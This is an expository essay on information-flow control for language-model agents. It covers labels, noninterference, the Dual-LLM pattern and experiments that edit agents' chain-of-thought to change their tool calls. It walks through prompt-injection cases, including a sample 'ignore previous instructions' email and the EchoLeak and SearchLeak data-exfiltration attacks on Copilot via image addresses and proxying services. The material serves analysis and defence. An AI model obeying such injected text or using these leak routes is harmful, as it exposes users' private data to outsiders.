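# Does separating reasoning from execution isolate influence in language model agents?

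## The claim, and the ideas needed to test it

In a language model agent, a language model chooses actions, such as reading a file or sending an email, and an ordinary program carries them out. The model only takes in and produces text. The program, called the harness, builds the model's input, parses its output and performs the requested actions. Agents read emails, web pages and documents that strangers can write, so their designers have to keep that text from steering the agent. Some designers rely on separation. *Parallax* (Fokou, 2026), for example, holds that the system that reasons about actions must be "structurally unable to execute them". Whether this separation also cuts off the influence of what the model has read is a question about information flow. Computer scientists developed most of the concepts needed to answer it between 1973 and 1982.

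### One email, one tool call

Take a request that Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use to illustrate the danger: summarise my recent emails about a project and send the summary to my manager. The harness first assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives for one response. Here it holds some standing instructions, the user's request and a description of the functions on offer. The model answers with a short piece of structured text such as `read_emails(number=3)`. This is a tool call, and so far nothing has happened in the mailbox. The harness parses the text, finds a function name and an argument in it, runs the function and appends the three emails to the context. Then it queries the model again, and the model emits a second tool call:

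```
send_message(to="manager@firm.example", message="Project X is two weeks late ...")
```

The harness parses that too and sends the message through the mail server. Engineers call this cycle the agent loop, and it repeats until the model produces a reply with no tool call.

A model produces only tokens, the word fragments in which it reads and writes, even when it calls a tool. Its part ends with the last token of the tool call, and execution begins when the harness treats some of those tokens as a request. In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) describes telling a model to write `action:search_email(...)` whenever it needs to search, then scanning its output for that pattern. His own simplified harness took only a few dozen lines of Python.

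Suppose that one of the three emails comes from a stranger and contains an order to ignore previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. If the model responds with a matching `send_message` call, a harness without further checks runs it and sends out the private email, even though the model never accessed the mail server directly.

### Three readings of "the model cannot act"

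The weakest reading of the sentence is that the model has no direct effect on the world. This is true of every agent by construction, even one that has just sent a private email to a stranger, so this reading cannot be used to distinguish safe designs from unsafe ones.

Authority confinement is the stronger requirement that the system never executes anything outside a fixed set of permitted actions. A component other than the model must enforce this by checking each tool call against the set before the harness runs it. In *Trident* (2026), a design for agents that revise their plans as they read, an administrator writes the outermost set in advance. One sample policy lets an office agent pay at most $5,000 to any of three vendors on file. The check blocks a payment to an unknown account but allows an extra payment to a listed vendor, even if the only reason for it is a line that an attacker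 inserted into an email. *Trident* therefore adds narrower policies for each task.

The most demanding reading is noninterference, which requires that changing the untrusted text cannot change what the agent does. Untrusted text is text that someone other than the user or the system's operator could have written or changed. One can test for noninterference by comparing two runs that differ only in the stranger's email. If the tool calls differ, the email had influence, even if every call is harmless and authorised.

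The absence of a direct effect implies neither confinement nor noninterference, because a harness can run whatever the model writes. Confinement doesn't imply noninterference, since the email can still determine which permitted action the agent takes. Noninterference doesn't imply confinement either. An agent that empties the mailbox after every request, whatever the emails contain, satisfies noninterference, and only a permission check would stop it. Such a fault can occur without an attacker, and Costa and colleagues point out that models misread their users and make needless calls even when all the data is trustworthy. *Trident* therefore has separate theorems for authority confinement and influence. The second gives a bound on influence, which reduces to noninterference only when the planning model may learn nothing from untrusted text.

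Computer security researchers have long pointed out the gap between permission and influence. Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, objected that most access controls govern immediate access to an object and ignore the paths information can take afterwards. Sabelfeld and Myers (2003), in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security*, observed that neither access control nor encryption directly enforces a policy about information flow.

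### Prompt injection

The stranger's email is an example of prompt injection, an attack in which text the agent was meant only to read changes what it does. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, trace the problem to a shared channel, in which instructions and data both reach the model as natural language in one context and nothing in the format distinguishes them. Willison calls the agent a confused deputy, an older security term for a program that someone with fewer rights tricks into misusing its own rights.

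An attack of this kind does not have to contain an instruction. Girrens and Wang describe an agent that retrieves an invoice and pays it, as the user intended, but the account number in the invoice belongs to the attacker. A filter that looks for suspicious commands would find none. Partly for this reason, many recent defences check the provenance of a text (where it came from) instead of its content, and treat everything from an untrusted source as potentially hostile.

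Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, argues that we should assume the worst case, in which any exposure to malicious tokens taints the whole output and whoever planted them also controls the tool calls. He was commenting on a paper of the same name by Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, whose guiding principle is that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must be unable to trigger any consequential action. The worst-case assumption is too pessimistic as a description of how models usually behave. In *Trident*'s experiments, an undefended agent running on Claude Sonnet 4.5 resisted every attack in AgentDojo, a standard test suite for prompt injection. But attacks from a second suite, built around tasks where an email has to shape the plan, still got through with all four models tested. The worst-case assumption is the right one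 for a guarantee, which has to hold against even the strongest attack.

### Labels and the join

To reason about provenance, we label each piece of data. The simplest useful scheme uses a confidentiality label, which records whether the data is public or secret, and an integrity label, which records whether its source is trusted or untrusted. In the scheme of Costa and colleagues, the user's request is by default trusted and public, a record from a company database is trusted and secret, and a page from the open web is untrusted and public. The four possible combinations are partly ordered, with untrusted secret data at the top because it needs the most care, and trusted public data at the bottom. Information may flow only upwards. The two combinations in the middle cannot be ranked against each other, because one is secret and the other comes from an untrusted source.

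These four labels form a lattice: an ordered set in which any two elements have a least upper bound. The least upper bound, or join, written ⊔, is the lowest label that lies at or above both. It is the label for anything derived from both. Suppose an agent summarises two emails. One comes from the company's payroll system and lists salaries, so it is trusted and secret. The other is a newsletter from outside, untrusted and public. The label of the summary is

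```
(trusted, secret) ⊔ (untrusted, public)
    = (trusted ⊔ untrusted, secret ⊔ public)
    = (untrusted, secret)
```

The summary gets this label, which neither email had, because it may reveal salaries and may also contain whatever the newsletter's writer wanted.

Denning showed why the label of a result should be the join of its inputs' labels. The label must be at least as high as that of each input. Otherwise, a system that forbids copying a secret number *a* into *c* could permit *c := a + b*, and anyone could make the copy by setting *b* to zero. The label should also be no higher than necessary. If *a* and *b* may each flow into *c* separately, then a value computed from both may flow there too. Only the least upper bound meets both requirements. Denning also made the combined label depend only on the inputs and not on the function, so the method was slightly overcautious from the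 beginning. For example, *a* multiplied by zero keeps the label of *a*, although the result reveals nothing.

Costa and colleagues also use finer labels, which are sets of people. If Ann, Bob and Cem may read one document, and Bob, Cem and Dee may read another, only Bob and Cem may read a summary of both. For integrity, the sets list possible writers, and the join is their union, because any of the four people could have influenced the summary.

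The integrity half of the scheme comes from K. J. Biba's *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* (1977), written at MITRE for the US Air Force. Military security had until then dealt with disclosure, but Biba addressed sabotage and graded information by the damage an unauthorised change could do. Under his strict integrity policy, which mirrors the rule for secrets, a program may read only information at least as trustworthy as itself and modify only information at most as trustworthy. Biba put the most trustworthy level at the top, so combined information took the minimum level of its sources. Recent agent designs reverse this scale so that "up" always means "more restricted" and one join operation works for both secrecy and integrity.

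In taint tracking, the system labels data where it enters, computes joins of the labels as programs copy and combine the data, and checks the result at each sink, a point where data has an effect outside the agent. A typical integrity check allows a consequential call only if its label is trusted. A typical confidentiality check allows an email to be sent only if all its recipients may read its contents. The confidentiality check limits what a stranger can gain through prompt injection but, as Costa and colleagues note, does not stop the injection on its own, because the stranger can still cause the email to be sent.

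### Noninterference as a formula

In *Security Policies and Security Models*, Goguen and Meseguer (1982) gave noninterference its standard definition. They model a system as a machine that receives commands from users and shows each user some output. One group of users does not interfere with another if the first group's commands have no effect on the output the second group can see.

For the formula, let *w* be any sequence of commands, each tagged with the user who issued it. Let out(*w*, *u*) be what user *u* sees after the machine has processed *w*, and let purge_G(*w*) be the same sequence without the commands of group *G*. Then *G* does not interfere with group *G′* when

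```
out(w, u) = out(purge_G(w), u)    for every sequence w and every user u in G′
```

Suppose the stranger is in *G* and the manager is in *G′*. In one history, the stranger sends an email and the user then asks the agent to forward the weekly report. We can delete the stranger's email, run everything again, and compare what the manager receives in each run. The formula holds only if the manager receives the same output in both runs, for this history and every other. One pair of runs with different outputs is enough to refute it, but no number of matching pairs can prove it, because other histories always remain untested. A claim of noninterference therefore needs a proof about the system, while a claim that an agent resisted a list of attacks needs only a test.

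Models usually pick their tokens partly at random, so two runs of an agent can differ even without an attacker. A test can account for this by holding the random choices fixed or by comparing the probability of each outcome. *Trident* covers both versions, and *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a probabilistic form of the property.

The other adjustment, which matters more in practice, is to require noninterference for only some of the agent's outputs. A useful summary of an inbox has to change when the emails change, so requiring noninterference between the emails and everything the agent produces would forbid the task. A sensible guarantee might protect which functions run and who receives the messages, but leave the wording of the messages open. A claim that untrusted text has no influence is therefore incomplete unless it specifies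 which text and which outputs it covers.

### Explicit and implicit flows

Information can travel through content or through a decision. In this program the email's text goes to the manager, which is an explicit flow:

```
text = email.body
send_message(to=manager, message=text)
```

In the next one it does not:

```
if "invoice" in email.body:
    send_message(to=manager, message="Please call me.")
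```

The writer of the email decided whether the message went out, so a manager who knows the program learns whether the email mentioned an invoice, even though none of the email's text reaches the manager. This is an implicit flow. It also occurs when no message is sent, since the absence of a message is informative. Denning, who introduced the terms explicit and implicit flow, used the statement `if a = 0 then b := c`. Information flows explicitly from *c* to *b* only when the assignment runs, but implicitly from *a* to *b* whether or not it runs.

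A taint tracker that follows only copying and arithmetic misses the email's influence in the second program, because the constant "Please call me." is fully trusted and public. Denning reports a remedy by Fenton, who gave a label to the program counter, the machine's record of its current place in the program. When the program enters a branch, the machine joins the condition's label to the program counter's label, and every statement inside the branch inherits the result. When the branch ends, the machine restores the earlier label. With this remedy, the message to the manager would carry the email's label and fail the check at the sink.

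Implicit flows are the usual case in an agent. A model that reads an email and then chooses the next tool call is branching on the email's text, with one branch for each tool call it could write. Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference, which would cover such decisions, would come close to banning every call that writes public data after any call that may have read secret data. They settle for a weaker confidentiality property, explicit secrecy, which covers direct flows of data but not what an observer could infer from the order of the calls.

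### The confinement problem

Before any of this theory existed, Lampson (1973) carefully examined the idea that isolating a program isolates its influence. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* describes a customer who runs somebody else's program on private data and wants to be sure that the program does not pass the data on to the program's owner.

Blocking unauthorised access is not enough, because the program needs the data to do its job. Lampson listed ways the program could leak the data. It can remember the data until its owner next calls it, write it to a file, or send it in a message. It can encode a few bits in the bill, which the owner must see to get paid. It can also vary its load on the machine, so that another program can read the signal from the machine's performance. He called paths of this last sort covert channels, since nobody intended them to carry information. Total isolation,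 under which a confined program calls no other program, would be sufficient, but Lampson judged it "quite impractical". He proposed letting the customer fix in advance what goes into the bill and the covert channels or, with less overhead, accepting some leakage and limiting its rate.

A language model without tools makes no calls, but two items on Lampson's list keep it from being totally isolated. One is the bill, a legitimate output that has to reach someone. A model's answer is the same kind of output and can carry far more information. The other is memory. Lampson's rules first require that a confined program keep no memory between calls. A model with fixed weights meets that requirement only until the harness gives it the conversation history, which the agent loop does at every step.

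A partial solution for ordinary programs soon followed. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977) described a check that can prove a program's public results do not depend on its confidential inputs. The check is simple enough for a compiler to perform, and it works because each statement in a program names the variables it uses.

### Why a model's output takes the label of its whole context

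No such list exists for a language model. It computes each new token from all the tokens before it, and any of them may have affected the choice. Nobody can tell from the weights which of forty messages a given tool call depends on. The safe label for a response is therefore the join of the labels of everything in the context. Costa and colleagues adopt this rule, arguing that labels cannot be tracked precisely through a model. Garby and colleagues similarly label a conversation with the upper bound of the labels of all the messages sent in it.

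The rule is often too cautious. If a model reads a newsletter and then adds two numbers for the user, its answer is labeled untrusted, even though the model probably didn't use the newsletter. Costa and colleagues mention a more precise method from Siddiqui and colleagues, which finds the messages that influenced a response, regenerates the response from those messages alone, and gives it their label. The new response is generated without the other messages, but the choice of which messages to keep may still depend on them.

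Suppose an agent's context starts out trusted and public. When the agent looks up a salary, the context becomes secret. When it opens a web page, the context also becomes untrusted. Every later tool call is then secret and untrusted, even one to book a meeting room, and nothing the agent reads later can make the label less restrictive. This is label creep, the tendency of labels to grow more restrictive until most useful actions are blocked. *Trident* gives a reason why agents suffer from it more than ordinary programs do. In a program, the branch eventually ends and Fenton's machine restores the old label, but an agent that replans after every observation never leaves the branch.

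Biba had found the same effect. One of the policies in MITRE's report lowers a program's integrity level to that of the least trustworthy thing it has read. He wrote that this had "rather disagreeable behavior" because a program could lose the right to modify objects it needed and could recover only by being restarted. His strict policy prevents the decline by blocking the read, so an email assistant could not open the email.

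Practical systems therefore make exceptions. Declassification treats some secret data as public, and endorsement treats some untrusted data as trusted. Each exception deliberately weakens noninterference, and how much depends on what may pass. A yes-or-no answer about an email carries at most one bit of influence, a choice among *k* categories carries at most log₂ *k* bits, and free text has no such limit.

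### The Dual-LLM pattern

Another way to keep the context clean is never to put untrusted text into it. Willison proposed this in 2023 as the Dual-LLM pattern. A privileged model receives the user's request and can call tools, but never receives untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools. An ordinary software controller sits between them.

If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model requests the email, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then asks for a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores its answer as `$VAR2`. Finally, the privileged model asks the controller to display `$VAR2`. It has seen the two variable names but none of the email. Willison allowed one exception, which is an early case of endorsement. The quarantined model may sort a text into one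 of a fixed set of categories, and the controller may pass the category to the privileged model after checking that it is valid.

The pattern cuts the implicit flow from the email to the choice of actions, but leaves open the explicit flow into the contents of those actions. The same division appears in a related design, which fixes the list of tool calls before any untrusted text arrives. In an example that Willison retells, an agent sends the day's schedule to the user's boss. A poisoned calendar entry can corrupt the body of that email, but it cannot change the recipient. If a tool call's argument is a bank account number taken from an invoice, a poisoned invoice could misdirect the payment without changing the plan.

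Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad". It complicates the software, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model undoes the protection. It also rules out tasks that require reading before planning. *Trident* gives the example of a forwarded email from a caterer, with a request to take care of what the email asks for. An agent that fixes its plan before reading the email is immune to the false bank details in it, but cannot do the job, because the job is described only in the email. In the extreme case of a request such as "Do what Jane's email says", no policy can always distinguish the user's intent from an attacker's.

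## Experiments that change an agent's reasoning text and watch what it does

The labelling rules and the Dual-LLM pattern both assume that the text in a model's context can determine its next tool call. Several recent studies measure how far this is true of the reasoning, or chain of thought, that a model writes for itself before it answers. A harness normally runs only the tool call that follows the reasoning and does not look for requests in the reasoning. If this separation from execution isolated influence, changing the reasoning would have little effect on what the agent does.

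### Two histories that differ in one word

In *Computation, Not Memory*, Mouseli and Moayedi (2026) gave two small open models, Qwen3-8B and Qwen3.5-9B, a file system to tidy. It holds three log files and a report, each locked or unlocked. The agent must move every unlocked log file to an archive and never touch a locked file. It issues one command per turn, such as `mv beta.log`, and the harness runs only the last line that starts with `CMD:`. The first message lists the state of every lock. Later messages sometimes announce that a background job has toggled a lock, without giving its new state.

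For their main test, the experimenters took saved conversations and made two copies of each. The copies differed only in whether the first message listed one log file as locked or unlocked, and nothing later in the conversation mentioned that file's lock. This gave 114 pairs for Qwen3-8B and 104 for Qwen3.5-9B. The model reasoned about each copy separately. The experimenters then swapped the reasoning, so that the locked-file conversation continued with the reasoning written for the unlocked-file one, and vice versa. The model then wrote only the command, always choosing the most probable next token so that random sampling did not affect the comparison.

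The table gives the number of pairs in which the model wrote a command to move the file.

| Reasoning supplied | Qwen3-8B, file locked | Qwen3-8B, file unlocked | Qwen3.5-9B, file locked | Qwen3.5-9B, file unlocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 4 | 18 | 9 | 31 |
| Own, for this history | 0 | 45 | 0 | 41 |
| Written for the other history | 43 | 2 or fewer | 41 | 2 or fewer |

Reasoning that favoured moving the file led the models to move it almost as often in the wrong history (43 of 114 pairs) as in the history it was written for (45). Both counts are low because the models often chose another command first, such as checking a lock, even when the file was unlocked. With the reasoning held fixed, changing the history changed whether the model moved the file in at most two pairs.

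The history still influenced the command, but almost entirely through the reasoning. When Qwen3-8B wrote its own reasoning, one changed word in the first message made the difference between 0 moves and 45. Correcting the history while leaving the old reasoning in place would have achieved very little. The rule that a model's output takes the label of its whole context therefore has to cover the reasoning too.

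The history still had a small direct effect. For Qwen3-8B, changing the history moved the average log-probability of the move command by 1.5 or 7.5, depending on which reasoning was in place, while changing the reasoning moved it by 15.7 or 9.7. So strict, probabilistic noninterference fails even with the reasoning fixed.

The effect came from the reasoning's content, not its length. On 400 other saved conversations per model, the model's own reasoning cut the share of attempted moves and deletions that targeted locked files from 49% to 6% for Qwen3-8B and from 40% to 4% for Qwen3.5-9B. A row of dots of the same length barely changed that share. An accurate table of all the locks reduced it less than the reasoning did, to 32% and 16%.

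Mouseli and Moayedi also reversed only the explicit statements about the lock in the reasoning, which changed whether the model moved the file in just one pair. After one such edit, Qwen3.5-9B's reasoning contained the line "alpha.log: unlocked (don't touch)", and the model did not move the file. The command apparently follows the plan at the end of the reasoning more than the facts stated before it. *Doing What They Say, Not What They Reason* (Wang, 2026) reports a similar pattern in a poker experiment. Claude Haiku 4.5, Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite and DeepSeek-Reasoner contradicted their explicitly stated decisions in only 0.7% to 1.8% of cases, but those decisions did not always follow from the reasons given. In one hand, Haiku should have raised according to its own estimates and stated rule, but it decided to call.

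The swap had less effect in one harder variant, where a background job had toggled the file's lock once. Qwen3-8B still followed the supplied reasoning, targeting the locked file in 39 of 122 pairs after a swap and in 4 with its own reasoning. Qwen3.5-9B targeted it in 12 of 303 pairs after a swap and in 7 with its own reasoning. This model moved the file in only 12 pairs even with its own reasoning for the unlocked version, so there was little behavior for a swap to transfer.

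### Influence over the text and permission to execute

The table counts commands that the model wrote, including attempts to move locked files, which always fail in this file system. The harness and the file system controlled what could be executed, but swapping the reasoning changed which command the model requested. Someone who can change the reasoning can therefore influence the action without having execution rights, because the harness runs the resulting command with the agent's rights.

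In the opposite swap, reasoning written for a locked file reduced Qwen3-8B's moves of an unlocked file from 45 to two or fewer. A permission check cannot prevent this, because an agent that fails to make a move it was supposed to make breaks no rule and gives the check no command to refuse. For an email assistant, the equivalent would be a stranger's message that stops the agent from forwarding a warning.

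### One inserted sentence

In *The Belief-Action Gap in Language Model Agents*, Okcu, Wang and colleagues (2026) found a similar dependence in a different model and task. Their agent, running on the open model gpt-oss-20b, sees a nine-by-nine text maze. It has to collect a key, pass through a locked door and reach a goal by moving left, right, up or down. The researchers paired the maze from one decision with reasoning from another decision that had led to a different move. They cut this reasoning off at about 10%, 50% or 90% of its length, forced the model to choose immediately, and measured the probability it gave each move.

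Across 396 such mismatched pairs, the model gave the move that went with the borrowed reasoning an average probability between 0.60 and 0.67, depending on the cut. It gave the move it had originally made in that maze between 0.13 and 0.17, less than the 0.25 expected from an even guess.

Adding one sentence to the model's reasoning was often enough to change its move. The experimenters stopped the model partway through its reasoning and added a remark that, on a second look at the grid, the correct move was the one it currently ranked second. When the model had given its original move a probability below 0.7, it switched to the suggested move every time. When that probability was 0.95 or more, it still switched in 62.5% of cases. A neutral sentence of similar form changed the choice in 9.6% of cases. Explicitly telling the model to disregard mismatched reasoning moved its choice to the intended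 action in only 1.0% of cases.

Okcu and colleagues also tried to change the choice by editing the network's activations, the numbers it computes while processing each token. They edited the last 12 or so tokens of the reasoning, where a classifier could tell fairly well how settled the decision was. Shifting these activations in a direction associated with a particular move produced that move in 3.6% of cases, no better than a random shift of equal size. Replacing all the activations in that window with those from another decision redirected the choice in 20.8% of cases. Okcu and colleagues caution that they tested only certain layers and kinds of edit, so a better-chosen edit might have worked.

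Esakkiraja, Akhiyarov and colleagues (2026), in *Therefore I am. I Think*, studied how Qwen3-4B and GLM-Z1-9B decide whether to call a tool or answer directly. A simple classifier predicted the decision with high accuracy from the model's activations before it had written any reasoning. Adding a corresponding direction to the activations flipped the decision in 7% to 79% of cases, depending on the model and the test set. For example, when a user asked for the song "Baby Shark" and the only tool was a volume control, the unedited Qwen3-4B explained that it could not play music. With its activations changed, the model reasoned its way to setting the volume to 100.

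In such cases the model's reasoning justifies a choice it was already inclined to make. The maze agent's preferred move also tended to settle early, typically about halfway through the reasoning and hundreds of tokens before it appeared in the text. An inserted sentence could still overturn that preference, so the text can strongly affect the choice even when the model leans towards a move early. But a defence that only inspects or cleans the reasoning would miss any influence an email has on the model before the reasoning begins.

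### When the model can go on reasoning

Forcing a choice immediately after an edit may exaggerate the edit's effect, because the model has no chance to reconsider. *Thought Branches* (Macar, Bogdan and colleagues, 2025) let models continue reasoning after an edit, in fictional scenarios where they could blackmail someone or expose private information. The inserted sentences expressed doubt, ethical concerns or other options. Sentences that were handwritten or copied from other contexts had almost no effect on what the models finally did. The models often ignored them or soon wrote something that replaced them. Sentences with the same meaning that the model produced when it resumed from that point had much larger effects, in some cases eliminating the blackmail. A clumsy insertion may therefore have little effect on an agent that reasons at length. Text that fits the model's own reasoning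 is harder for it to discard. The swapped reasoning in the file task was close to this kind, since the same model had written it for an almost identical conversation.

The strength of the effect also depends on what other information the model has. *Altered Thoughts, Altered Actions* (Trinh, Azam and colleagues, 2026) tested DeepThinkVLA, a model that looks at camera images, writes a few sentences of reasoning and then controls a simulated robot arm. Replacing the object names in the reasoning while leaving the user's instruction intact lowered the success rate by 20.8 percentage points on ten tasks. When the instruction was corrupted instead, supplying correct reasoning recovered 47.8 points. All ten tasks take place in the same scene, so the model can identify the task only from language.

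Karnik, Lee and colleagues (2026), in *When Reasoning Helps Action*, found that the same model's actions depended much less on its reasoning. They raised the accuracy of its statements about whether the gripper was holding an object from 69.3% to 90.2%, but its success at the tasks hardly changed. The camera images probably already showed most of what those statements described. But in a driving model, better reasoning reduced collisions by 30.4% on a set of difficult routes. An email agent is closer to the first robot experiment, since it receives nearly all its information about the task as text.

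### From edited reasoning to a stranger's document

In all the swaps and insertions above, the experimenters wrote directly into the model's reasoning. The server's operator or anyone who has broken into the server can do this, but the sender of an email cannot. Trinh and colleagues describe the minimum requirement as "an adversary with write access to text, and nothing else". The opportunity is narrower for proprietary models. *Can Reasoning Models Detect Changes to their Chains of Thought?* (Napa, Singh and colleagues, 2026) points out that the public interfaces to the leading ones do not let customers supply the reasoning. Four large open models do allow it, but even after a warning that someone might have changed their reasoning, they usually detected edits only slightly better than chance, including when the experimenters had deleted the whole second half.

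An outside attacker has to write a document that leads the model to produce the desired reasoning itself. Neither the file experiment nor the maze experiment tested this. Both used small artificial tasks and modest-sized models, so their percentages are weak evidence of how often a real attack on a commercial assistant would succeed.

Another experiment by Macar and colleagues comes closer, because the influence started in the prompt. They gave a 14-billion-parameter model multiple-choice questions with a hint that a professor favoured a particular wrong answer. For 40 questions on which the hint was effective, they selected reasoning that led to the hinted answer without mentioning the hint. They then deleted the hint from the prompt, kept the opening sentences of that reasoning and let the model continue from there, 100 times for each cut-off point. The model still chose the hinted answer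 more often than it otherwise would, and this tendency grew as it received more of the old reasoning. No single sentence accounted for most of the effect. Removing a suspicious text after a model has reasoned about it may therefore leave its influence in place, and a search of the reasoning for traces of that text could find nothing.

Reasoning text can also influence later responses, because many harnesses keep the model's earlier replies in the context, and these often contain short notes about what it has worked out. Mouseli and Moayedi tested 75 cases in which such a note correctly described a file as unlocked and a later event then locked it. Without fresh reasoning, Qwen3-8B tried to move the locked file in 10 cases when the harness had kept only its earlier commands, and in 31 when it had kept the notes as well. Keeping the notes did not increase Qwen3.5-9B's errors (20 cases without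 them and 17 with them). Fresh reasoning reduced Qwen3-8B's errors only from 31 to 21, because the model sometimes failed to take the new event into account.

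## EchoLeak: a chat assistant that leaked data by writing text

The agents in the file and maze experiments wrote commands, which a harness then ran, but EchoLeak, an attack on the chat assistant Microsoft 365 Copilot, needed no command. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security discovered that an outsider could send an employee one email and later receive private data from that employee's Copilot session. Copilot could not send emails on its own (Reddy and Gujral, 2025, *EchoLeak*). The model only wrote an answer that contained the address of an image, and other programs sent the data out.

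### From the inbox to the outsider's server

*Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is the discoverers' account. When an employee asks Copilot a question, a search component looks through the employee's mailbox, files and chats and the company's internal sites, and adds whatever seems relevant to the model's context. Although only employees could ask Copilot questions, anyone could add text to the material it searched by sending an email.

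Suppose an employee asks about the company's rules on leave. The outsider's email appears to cover that subject, so the search component retrieves it along with internal documents. Microsoft used a classifier to screen the model's input for prompt injection, but the email read like ordinary business mail and the classifier did not flag it. The email contained instructions to find the most sensitive item in the context and put it in an image address, and the model followed them.

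An image in a chat answer begins as text giving the address where the picture is stored. The address can have extra characters at the end, which the server usually records when a browser requests the picture. Microsoft had a filter that removed outside addresses from Copilot's answers, but the filter did not recognise every way of writing one. When the employee's browser displayed the answer, it tried to load the picture.

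Another defence, a content security policy, listed the domains from which the page could load images. It stopped the browser from contacting the outsider's server directly, but the list included a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch other addresses on request. The browser contacted Teams, Teams contacted the outsider's server, and that server recorded the private data. Reddy and Gujral write that the employee would have seen only what looked like a broken image. The answer did not cite the email, because the email contained an instruction to the model not to mention it.

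The table lists the component that acted at each step and the label of the data it handled. The labels come from the four-label lattice of Costa and colleagues.

| Step | Component that acted | Label of the data |
|---|---|---|
| Deliver the outsider's email | Mail server | Untrusted, public |
| Put the email and internal files into one context | Search component | Untrusted, secret |
| Write an answer with an image address in it | Model | Untrusted, secret |
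| Check the answer for outside addresses | Output filter | Untrusted, secret |
| Request the image | Browser | Untrusted, secret |
| Pass the request on | Teams service | Untrusted, secret |
| Record the address | Outsider's server | Untrusted, secret, now in an outsider's hands |

The label changes only once, when the search component combines the two sources, and no later component does anything that would justify lowering it. The leak required both halves of the label, because the email determined where the image address pointed and the internal files supplied the data it contained. The outsider would have learned only that someone had displayed the answer if the address had contained no private data, and nothing if the address, even with private data in it, had pointed to a server inside the company.

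### Rendering as a sink

Showing the answer to the employee broke no rule, since the employee was allowed to read the files. But the browser first had to convert the answer into a displayed page, a process called rendering, and browsers request any images they find while doing this. Rendering can therefore send data out of the company, so it is a sink in the same sense as `send_message`. A designer who treats the screen as the end of the path will overlook this sink and consider only the employee, who is authorised to read the data.

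Microsoft already knew that images could leak data, because it had blocked an earlier leak of this kind reported by the security researcher Johann Rehberger (Microsoft, 2025). However, the filter and the content security policy checked only how an address was written and which domain it named. None of the defences that Ravia describes checked whether the answer drew on secret files, or whether the final recipient of the request was allowed to read them.

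The flaw's official classification also points to this step. The public vulnerability record, which GCVE (2025) reproduces, lists the flaw as a failure to neutralise special elements in "Output Used by a Downstream Component".

A list of permitted tool calls would not have helped, because the model called no sending tool. Copilot was allowed to search the files, the model was allowed to answer, and the browser was allowed to load images from Teams. The claim that the model could not act remained true throughout the attack, but a claim about influence is useful only if the system's boundary includes whatever interprets its text. In terms of Goguen and Meseguer's formula, the outputs an outsider can see include requests that reach the outsider's server, even if a browser makes them after the model has finished. A proof that covered only the model and its harness would have missed those requests.

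### Other readers that act on text

Like browsers, some messaging apps do this. PromptArmor, a security company, points out that apps such as Telegram and Slack fetch a preview of any link in a message. An agent that answers through such an app can leak data as soon as its reply appears, even if the user clicks nothing.

Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, describes a similar flaw from May 2026 in Copilot Cowork, another Microsoft product. Its agents could email the user's own inbox without approval. The inbox displayed images from external servers in those emails, so opening a message could send data to an attacker even though the user was its only recipient.

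The same reasoning applies to a build system, the software that turns source files into a running program. It executes commands in some of those files, so an agent that is only allowed to edit files can still cause commands to run at the next build. Another agent may read the first agent's answer and write a tool call in response. People also act on text when they click a link or follow advice.

These readers differ in how predictably they act. A browser loads every image that its rules allow, so an attacker can rely on it. A person or another model may ignore the text or become suspicious. A window that shows only plain characters makes no requests. Whether a piece of output is equivalent to a tool call therefore depends on what its reader does automatically and who can observe the result.

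### Report, repair and severity

Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, reports that Aim found the flaw in January 2025 and contacted Microsoft. Microsoft tried to fix it in April but found more problems in May. Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss said the whole repair took five months, which he considered very long for a flaw of this kind. Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft made the final fix on its own servers in May. The flaw became public on 11 June 2025 as CVE-2025-32711, its number in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities.

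Microsoft gave EchoLeak a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 (critical), and the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 (high). The scores differ because Microsoft judged that the damage could extend beyond the vulnerable component and that the attack had a small effect on integrity, while the database counted neither. The first disagreement is about where the system's boundary lies.

A Microsoft spokesperson told Goldman that the company had addressed the issue "before our customers were impacted", and the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded no exploitation. EchoLeak is therefore a demonstration by researchers. It shows that a leak was possible in a widely used product, but not how often one would have happened. Ravia reports that Copilot retrieved the test email for questions on various topics, but gives no success rate for the retrieval or for the whole attack. A lack of customer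 complaints would by itself be weak evidence that no data was stolen, because a victim would have had little to notice.

The discoverers and outside commentators also disagree about how new the attack was. Ravia proposed the term "LLM scope violation" for cases where untrusted instructions make a model use trusted data. Willison (2025) saw no need for a new term and considered EchoLeak an extended variant of a leak already known from a dozen products.

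### SearchLeak and the leaks that followed

A month after the disclosure, Microsoft wrote that when it fixes a reported flaw, it also protects against "the general class of issues, including variants". Later discoveries in the same product let us check how far this succeeded.

The security company Varonis published one of them on 15 June 2026. Its *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack on Copilot's enterprise search in which the attacker puts a search request in a link to a genuine Microsoft address. When an employee clicks the link, Copilot treats the request as instructions, searches the employee's mailbox and writes an answer with an image address that includes the title of an email. The title can contain a security code for logging in to another service.

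Copilot had a defence against images in answers, which converted the finished answer into a form that the browser would show as plain text. But the browser displayed the answer while the model was still writing it, and requested the image before the conversion. The content security policy failed much as it had in EchoLeak, because it allowed requests to Microsoft's search engine Bing, and the servers for Bing's image search then fetched the attacker's address. Varonis concludes that software must clean a model's output while rendering it, not afterwards.

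In EchoLeak the attacker's text came from the mailbox, but in SearchLeak it arrived where the user's own question normally goes. Taint tracking works only if data is labeled correctly when it enters, and a system that labels everything in the user's question as trusted would have mislabeled the attacker's instructions.

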